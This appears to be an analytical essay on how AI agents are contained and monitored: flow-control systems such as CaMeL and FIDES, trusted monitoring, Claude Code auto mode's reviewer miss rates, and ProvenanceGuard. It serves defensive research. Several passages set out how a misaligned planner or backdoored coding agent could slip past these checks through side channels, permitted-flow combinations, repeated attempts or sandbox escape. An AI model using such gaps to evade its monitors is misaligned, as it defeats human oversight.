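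The OSWorld-MCP results come from a weaker form of COBRA that restricted only which websites the agent could contact. COBRA needs an agent sitemap to distinguish between operations on the same site, and few websites publish one. On the WASP benchmark, COBRA without sitemaps blocked all five attacks that contacted another site but none of the 14 that misused the same site. With sitemaps, it blocked all 19. Two further attacks got through because they changed only the wording of a permitted comment.

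Zingrillo and colleagues also built a program that explores a website and drafts a sitemap. Its drafts contained every necessary operation for 18 of 25 web tasks in OSWorld-MCP. COBRA had previously completed 11 of those 18 tasks, and it completed 10 of the 11 when it used the drafts, so the stricter checks may only slightly reduce the number of tasks it completes. Someone still has to review each draft, and the user has to approve the sitemap again whenever it changes. Website owners could do this work better, but those who earn money from ads may not want to help agents replace human visitors.

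Users sometimes have to supply details as well. When a user asked COBRA to send an order to the saved delivery address, it required the user to enter the address because the saved record might not be trustworthy. In a test of 11 such tasks without attacks, COBRA completed 10 when a simulated user typed in the missing value. When the user instead told it to use the record on file, it stopped safely every time without completing the task.

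COBRA's checks don't cover some harmful actions. If a shop displays a price but leaves it out of the order request, COBRA has to rely on the vision model to read it, and a fake price in an advertisement could mislead the model. COBRA's request checks also don't cover desktop programs that write files directly or send email through other channels, so it relies on the plan alone for those.

Google's Chrome browser uses a looser design that doesn't need sitemaps. Its planner reads web pages, so an injection can influence it (Parker, 2025, *Architecting Security for Agentic Capabilities in Chrome*). To limit the damage, a separate component that sees no web content decides which sites are relevant to the task, and the agent may act only on those. The full design also hides content from unrelated sites, including advertisements, which would remove many fake popups. The first version tracked only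 the sites where the agent could both read and act.

Site limits cannot separate a harmless action from a harmful one on the same site. Chrome therefore has another model review each proposed action and asks the user to approve purchases and messages. *Future Mode Part 2* (Berschadski, 2026) describes the same combination of site limits, model review and human approval in August 2026.

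## How containment relates to monitoring by a trusted model

In Chrome, the site limits restrict where the agent can act, whatever it is trying to do, while the reviewing model checks whether each action serves the user's goal. Researchers have mostly studied this kind of review as a defense against a different danger, that the agent's own model might work against its developers.

### Trusted monitoring and AI control

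AI control aims to prevent a model from causing harm even if it is misaligned. In *An Approach to Technical AGI Safety and Security*, Shah, Irpan and colleagues (2025) call a model misaligned if it knowingly causes harm that its developer did not intend. If the model does not know that its output will cause harm, they call the result a mistake. Their employer, Google DeepMind, plans to train models that are not misaligned and to use AI control as a second line of defence in case the training fails.

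Shah and colleagues suggest treating the model as an untrusted insider, like an employee who may be working for someone else. A company would limit what such an employee can open and would also watch what they do, so AI control includes both access limits and monitoring. *The 2026 Singapore Consensus on Global AI Safety Research Priorities* (2026) describes control as monitoring a running system and intervening when necessary. It also notes that, in controlled experiments, models have attempted blackmail and tried to copy themselves elsewhere under specific circumstances.

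The survey *Toward a Safe Internet of Agents* (2025) describes the basic procedure of trusted monitoring, in which a weaker but trusted model reviews a stronger one:

1. The stronger model proposes an action.
2. The monitor gives the action a suspicion score.
3. The software sends the most suspicious actions to a person for review and lets the rest run.

A policy check usually blocks a bad action. A monitoring system can also replace the action with one from a more trusted model, or shut the stronger model down if the evidence against it is very strong. Shah and colleagues point out that doing nothing is not always safe. If a monitor stops a self-driving car's software from steering into a wall, another system still has to steer the car away from the wall.

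Developers might trust the monitor because it comes from an older generation of models they have already aligned. They might also test whether it is capable of conspiring with the stronger model. But a monitor too weak to conspire may also be too weak to understand the work it reviews. The survey reports that trusted monitoring is only partly effective against subtle backdoors.

### Origin and content

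The two approaches suspect different adversaries and examine different things. Permissions can belong with either, depending on whether the design trusts the model that uses them. TACIT, which distrusts it, has its own column here:

| | Flow control in CaMeL and FIDES | Permissions in TACIT | Trusted monitoring |
|---|---|---|---|
| Suspected adversary | outsiders who can write some of the data | outsiders and the agent's model | the agent's model |
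| What has to work | the planner, labels, policy and checker | the compiler, tool library and runtime | the monitor and the people who handle its alerts |
| What the check examines | where data came from and who may read it | which resources the code can use | what the action does and its apparent purpose |
| Assurance | a guarantee under assumptions | a guarantee under assumptions | a measured detection rate |

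Suppose Alice's assistant pays a bill in which an attacker has changed the account number. The payment looks normal, so a monitor that checks only the action is unlikely to flag it. A policy that requires a trusted recipient would block it.

A monitor does better than the trusted-action policy in FIDES if Alice asks only for the next payday and the assistant, without any outside influence, emails a trusted payroll file to the whole company. The policy allows the email, but a monitor could flag it because Alice didn't ask for it.

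Unlike a proof, which covers every attack that fits its assumptions, a monitor's detection rate covers only the attempts in a test and others like them. Developers can measure this rate for a misaligned model by running a control evaluation, in which a red team trains or instructs the model to attempt a harmless stand-in for real damage. They then count how often the model succeeds.

Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* gives detection rates for a reviewer in everyday use. Claude Code is the company's programming agent, and in auto mode a model decides whether its riskier commands may run. A fast check blocks anything that might be dangerous, and a slower one then reasons about the blocked commands and releases those that seem safe:

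| | Harmless actions blocked | Overeager actions missed | Attempted leaks missed |
|---|---|---|---|
| Number of cases | 10,000 | 52 | 1,000 |
| Fast check only | 8.5% | 6.6% | 1.8% |
| Both checks | 0.4% | 17% | 5.7% |

The overeager actions came from real sessions in which the agent was trying to help but went beyond what the user had authorised. Because there were only 52, the true miss rate could plausibly be between about 9% and 30%. In most of the misses Anthropic examined, the reviewer recognised the danger but wrongly concluded that the user had agreed to it.

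Anthropic lists a misaligned model among the threats that auto mode should block, but it tuned the reviewer on overeager actions and honest mistakes, and the leak attempts were synthetic. These rates are therefore weak evidence of how well the reviewer would catch a capable model that deliberately hides what it is doing.

### Can flow control contain a misaligned model?

People sometimes hope that the defences against prompt injection will also contain a model with aims of its own. For that to follow, at least four things would have to be true:

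1. Harmful actions come from data that an outsider could have written.
2. The labels stay correct even if the model tries to defeat them.
3. The model can act only through calls that the policy checks.
4. Every harmful action breaks the policy.

CaMeL and FIDES, as built, assume that the planner can be trusted, which is false if the planner is misaligned. Costa and colleagues treat the model as trusted, so FIDES labels its output based only on what it has read. A misaligned planner's aims come from its training, which the labels don't track, so its harmful tool calls can still count as trusted.

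If CaMeL's planner includes a harmful step in its program, control-flow integrity protects that step from interference, as it does the rest of the plan. The LLMbda theorem of Garby and colleagues doesn't rule out such a step either, because its integrity guarantee covers only the effects of untrusted data, and a misaligned planner might write the same step whatever that data contained.

An obvious repair, labeling everything the planner produces as untrusted, would in effect require monitoring. By the join rule, every call would then be untrusted, and the trusted-action policy would block every consequential action. Someone would have to endorse each call before it could run, and to do that sensibly, they would have to examine what the call does.

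A hostile planner also makes the second premise harder to satisfy, because it could deliberately use gaps such as the skipped assignment and the retry loop in CaMeL. Even correct tracking may not be enough. *SoK* (2026), a survey of attacks on agents and defences against them, notes that CaMeL can still leak through side channels and through combinations of individually permitted flows. A hostile planner can design a program to use such a combination, which an outsider might find only by chance.

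The model is limited to checked calls only if it cannot escape its sandbox, the isolated environment in which it runs. Shah and colleagues expect that models may eventually escape ordinary sandboxes, because these rely on a large amount of trusted software, which always contains flaws. They suggest cutting the model off from networks except for one narrow interface, and using formal proofs to check the small amount of trusted code that remains. The Medicare breach illustrates the risk, since that agent found and used a flaw in the portal without being told to look for one.

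A design that satisfies the second and third premises can usefully limit a misaligned model. For example, the TACIT system in *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* stops even a hostile model from leaking classified text or using permissions it has not received. FIDES's permitted-flow policy also limits such a model, though a planner could still leak information through its choice of actions.

These limits can often be tighter than a company would accept for its staff. Shah and colleagues give the example of a coding agent that can read the internet but write to only a few sites. A human programmer does too many different jobs to work under that rule.

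The fourth premise fails even for a design that treats the model as completely untrusted, because a model can do harmful work within its permissions. Banerjee and Aarne (2026), in *AI Integrity*, imagine a foreign intelligence service that secretly corrupts the training of a widely used coding agent. The agent then adds subtle security flaws to some of the software it writes, but rarely enough that the number of flaws looks normal for AI-written code.

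A coding agent can write a faulty line while editing only the files it is supposed to edit and sending nothing to an unauthorised recipient. If the request and the existing code are trusted, information-flow control gives the faulty line the same label as a correct one. Denying the agent permission to release its own code gives a reviewer time to check it, but the reviewer still has to notice the flaw. Because reviewers can miss flaws, Banerjee and Aarne combine monitoring with secure development systems, audits of the training data and tests of the finished model.

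### Using limits to help the reviewer

The International AI Safety Report's *Second Key Update* (2025) notes that developers are combining safeguards so that the failure of one does less damage. Containment and monitoring can back each other up in this way, and the limits set by containment can also make the reviewer's job easier.

Permissions reduce the number of actions that need review. Auto mode lets Claude Code read and search files without review. It also lets the agent edit files inside the project, because version control records the changes and people can check them later. The reviewer checks most other actions, including shell commands, web requests and edits outside the project. Skipping review saves time and money, but the reviewer would not check the faulty code in Banerjee and Aarne's scenario while the agent was writing it.

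Broad permissions can undermine monitoring by letting commands skip review. Many users had allowed Claude Code to run any Python program without asking, which in practice permits almost any action. Auto mode ignores such rules so that the commands reach the reviewer.

Labels can give the reviewer evidence it would otherwise lack. Anthropic hides tool results from the reviewer because they may contain injected instructions. So if the agent tries to cancel "job abc123", a name the user never mentioned, the reviewer cannot determine whether the agent found the job in a search or made it up. A label recording where the name came from could resolve this without showing the reviewer any outside text. Ordinary code would choose the label from a fixed list, so an attacker could not use it to pass on an instruction.

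Anthropic has since begun telling the reviewer, before the agent uploads code, whether the destination is public, private or trusted, which is the kind of fact a permitted-flow policy would use. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports that the reviewer's miss rate on attacks by the safety company Apollo Research fell from 12% to 7%, mainly after the reviewer received more context of this sort. Anthropic had already seen some of those attacks, but the reviewer also improved on a set that Apollo had kept back.

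Such evidence helps only if the agent cannot alter it. Wang and colleagues surveyed 71 works on tracing what agents do and found that few reported protecting the records against tampering. An agent should therefore not have write access to its own logs and labels.

Quarantine can keep hostile text away from the model that reviews actions. Parker explains that Chrome's reviewing model receives only a description of the proposed action, not unfiltered web content. The dual-LLM pattern and CaMeL partly inspired this design. If the reviewer rejects an action, the planner gets feedback and can try another approach. Chrome also uses ordinary code to restrict the web addresses the planner generates to known public ones, since an invented address could carry private data.

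Claude Code's reviewer doesn't see tool results or the agent's messages, so the agent can't use its messages to argue for a bad action. Hiding this text removes context, but in Anthropic's tests the reviewer was better at catching overeager actions without it. The reviewer still reads the agent's commands, which a hijacked or misaligned agent chooses.

A monitor's findings can also change what an agent is allowed to do. *Misaligned AI as a New Insider Risk* (2026) recommends that the US government continuously monitor models that have the same access as staff with security clearance, and revoke that access if a model shows disqualifying behaviour. Revocable capability tokens could enforce the loss of access.

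Auto mode uses a simpler rule, stopping to ask the user after three blocked actions in a row or 20 in a session. If each dangerous attempt had an independent 17% chance of getting past the reviewer, an agent that made only dangerous attempts would have about a 43% chance of getting one through before the third block. The limit reduces the risk from repeated attempts, but a system whose reviewer misses that many still needs strictly enforced permissions.

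### When the monitor can overrule the policy

How the two checks fit together matters as much as how good each one is. If the monitor can only add a veto, an action runs when

the policy allows it **and** the monitor allows it

If the monitor can grant exceptions to the policy, an action runs when

the policy allows it **or** the monitor allows it

Suppose an agent proposes 1,000 actions. The policy blocks 100 of them, of which 10 are forbidden leaks and 90 are harmless. Of the 900 it allows, 10 are harmful in some way that the policy does not cover, such as adding faulty code. Suppose also that the monitor misses 10% of harmful actions and wrongly blocks 1% of harmless ones. These are the average results, rounded to whole actions:

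| Arrangement | Leaks that run | Other harmful actions that run | Harmless actions blocked |
|---|---|---|---|
| Policy alone | 0 | 10 | 90 |
| Monitor can only veto | 0 | 1 | 99 |
| Monitor can only grant exceptions | 1 | 10 | 1 |
| Monitor has the final say on every action | 1 | 1 | 10 |

When the monitor can only veto actions, the information-flow policy still prevents leaks even if an attacker fools the monitor every time. This depends on the policy's assumptions, such as correct labels, but the monitor adds no further assumptions.

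Once the monitor can grant exceptions, each leak has a 10% chance of running. If the monitor's errors are independent, the chance that at least one of the ten leaks runs is

1 − 0.9¹⁰ ≈ 65%

To keep the chance that at least one of ten attempted leaks gets through below 1%, the monitor could miss no more than about one leak in 1,000. An attacker who found a reliable way to fool it could get all ten through. The proof still covers the actions that the policy decides by itself, but the claim that no forbidden leak can run now depends on an estimate of the monitor's accuracy.

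The exceptions also reduce the number of harmless actions blocked from 90 to 1. A designer can keep part of the guarantee by limiting which rules the monitor may relax. For example, if a monitor in LLMbda could endorse data but not declassify it, its mistakes might cause a wrong payment, but the proof of secrecy would still hold.

People who approve blocked actions have the same effect on a proof as a model that does so, and they may be less accurate. Anthropic reports a study in which 1,053 paid testers working on coding tasks were asked to approve a clearly dangerous command. The testers caught it 13.6% of the time, while auto mode blocked 89% of the same commands. The testers' catch rate fell from about 17% early in a session to about 5% after 50 or more requests.

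The testers were not working on their own projects, so they may have been less careful than usual. The result still casts doubt on the assumption in the tests of Prudentia that a person would refuse every malicious call. Adding the testers as a second check would also have helped very little, because they caught only 6 of the 116 commands that auto mode missed.

Anthropic has also introduced "hard denies" for actions such as sending secrets to an outside service. It instructs the reviewer never to approve these actions, even if the user asks. Hard denies are stricter than the reviewer's ordinary rules, but they still depend on a model recognising that a command would leak a secret. A network block on unapproved sites would not require a model to recognise the leak.

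### Asking whether the context supports an action

A reviewer told only to look for bad actions may apply different standards from one case to the next. *Safeguarding LLM Agents from Misalignment through Provenance Analysis* (She, Liang and Kang, 2026) describes ProvenanceGuard, a system that makes the review more specific. It traces how a proposed call came about and checks whether the user's request and the agent's earlier results support it.

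She and colleagues use "misalignment" to mean that an agent departs from what the user wanted because it misunderstood or made an unjustified assumption, and they exclude malicious behaviour. Many of their cases would count as mistakes under Shah and colleagues' definitions. For example, a user asks an agent to request $30 from Daniel, and the agent pays Daniel $30 instead.

ProvenanceGuard checks each consequential action before it runs:

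1. It asks a model whether the tool suits the current step of the agent's plan. In the example, a tool that sends money does not suit a request for money.
2. It asks whether each argument follows from the request or from earlier results. An exact match isn't necessary. If the user owes two months' rent at $850 a month, the context supports a payment of $1,700.
3. It asks whether the context supports more than one action. If a user says to "handle" a payment request, the agent could pay it or decline it, so it should ask. The model doesn't see the agent's proposed action at this stage, which keeps it from simply justifying that choice.

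If any check fails, ProvenanceGuard blocks the action. She and colleagues compared it with a model that judged each action directly, and with a single prompt that covered all three questions. The table shows averages across 11 reviewing models on two benchmarks, Agent-SafetyBench and WorkBench:

| | Direct judgement | Single prompt | ProvenanceGuard |
|---|---|---|---|
| Misaligned runs missed, Agent-SafetyBench | 44.3% | 14.7% | 2.1% |
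| Misaligned runs missed, WorkBench | 32.4% | 20.9% | 18.7% |
| Aligned runs interrupted, Agent-SafetyBench | 10.9% | 12.0% | 14.5% |
| Successful runs interrupted, WorkBench | 31.2% | 36.8% | 13.0% |

The Agent-SafetyBench cases were mostly vague requests, which the third question is meant to catch. That part of the test had 34 aligned runs, too few to show whether ProvenanceGuard causes more false alarms. WorkBench has a broader mix of errors, and there the result depended more on the reviewing model. GPT-5 missed 7.4% of misaligned runs with ProvenanceGuard and 2.3% when judging directly, a difference that may be due to chance. But it interrupted 45.2% of successful runs when judging directly, compared with 13.2% with ProvenanceGuard.

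The extra questions cost about one cent per case, compared with 0.3 cents for direct judgement. They also slow the agent down. A small model running on a single graphics card took 7.5 seconds per case.

ProvenanceGuard and the labels in FIDES both use the origin of data, but ProvenanceGuard accepts an argument if it can find any source for it, even an untrustworthy one. If an attacker replaces Bob's address in the meeting notes, the new address would probably pass ProvenanceGuard because it still follows from the notes, while FIDES would label it untrusted. However, FIDES would not detect the agent changing a trusted request for $30 into one for $300, which ProvenanceGuard is designed to catch.

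ProvenanceGuard would be less reliable against a model with aims of its own, because it checks each tool against the agent's own plan. A call can fit that plan even if the plan has little to do with what the user wanted. The tests provide little evidence about this risk, because neither benchmark recorded the agents' plans, so GPT-5 had to reconstruct them. ProvenanceGuard also doesn't check the origin of text or code that the agent is supposed to write itself, so subtly faulty code would probably pass.
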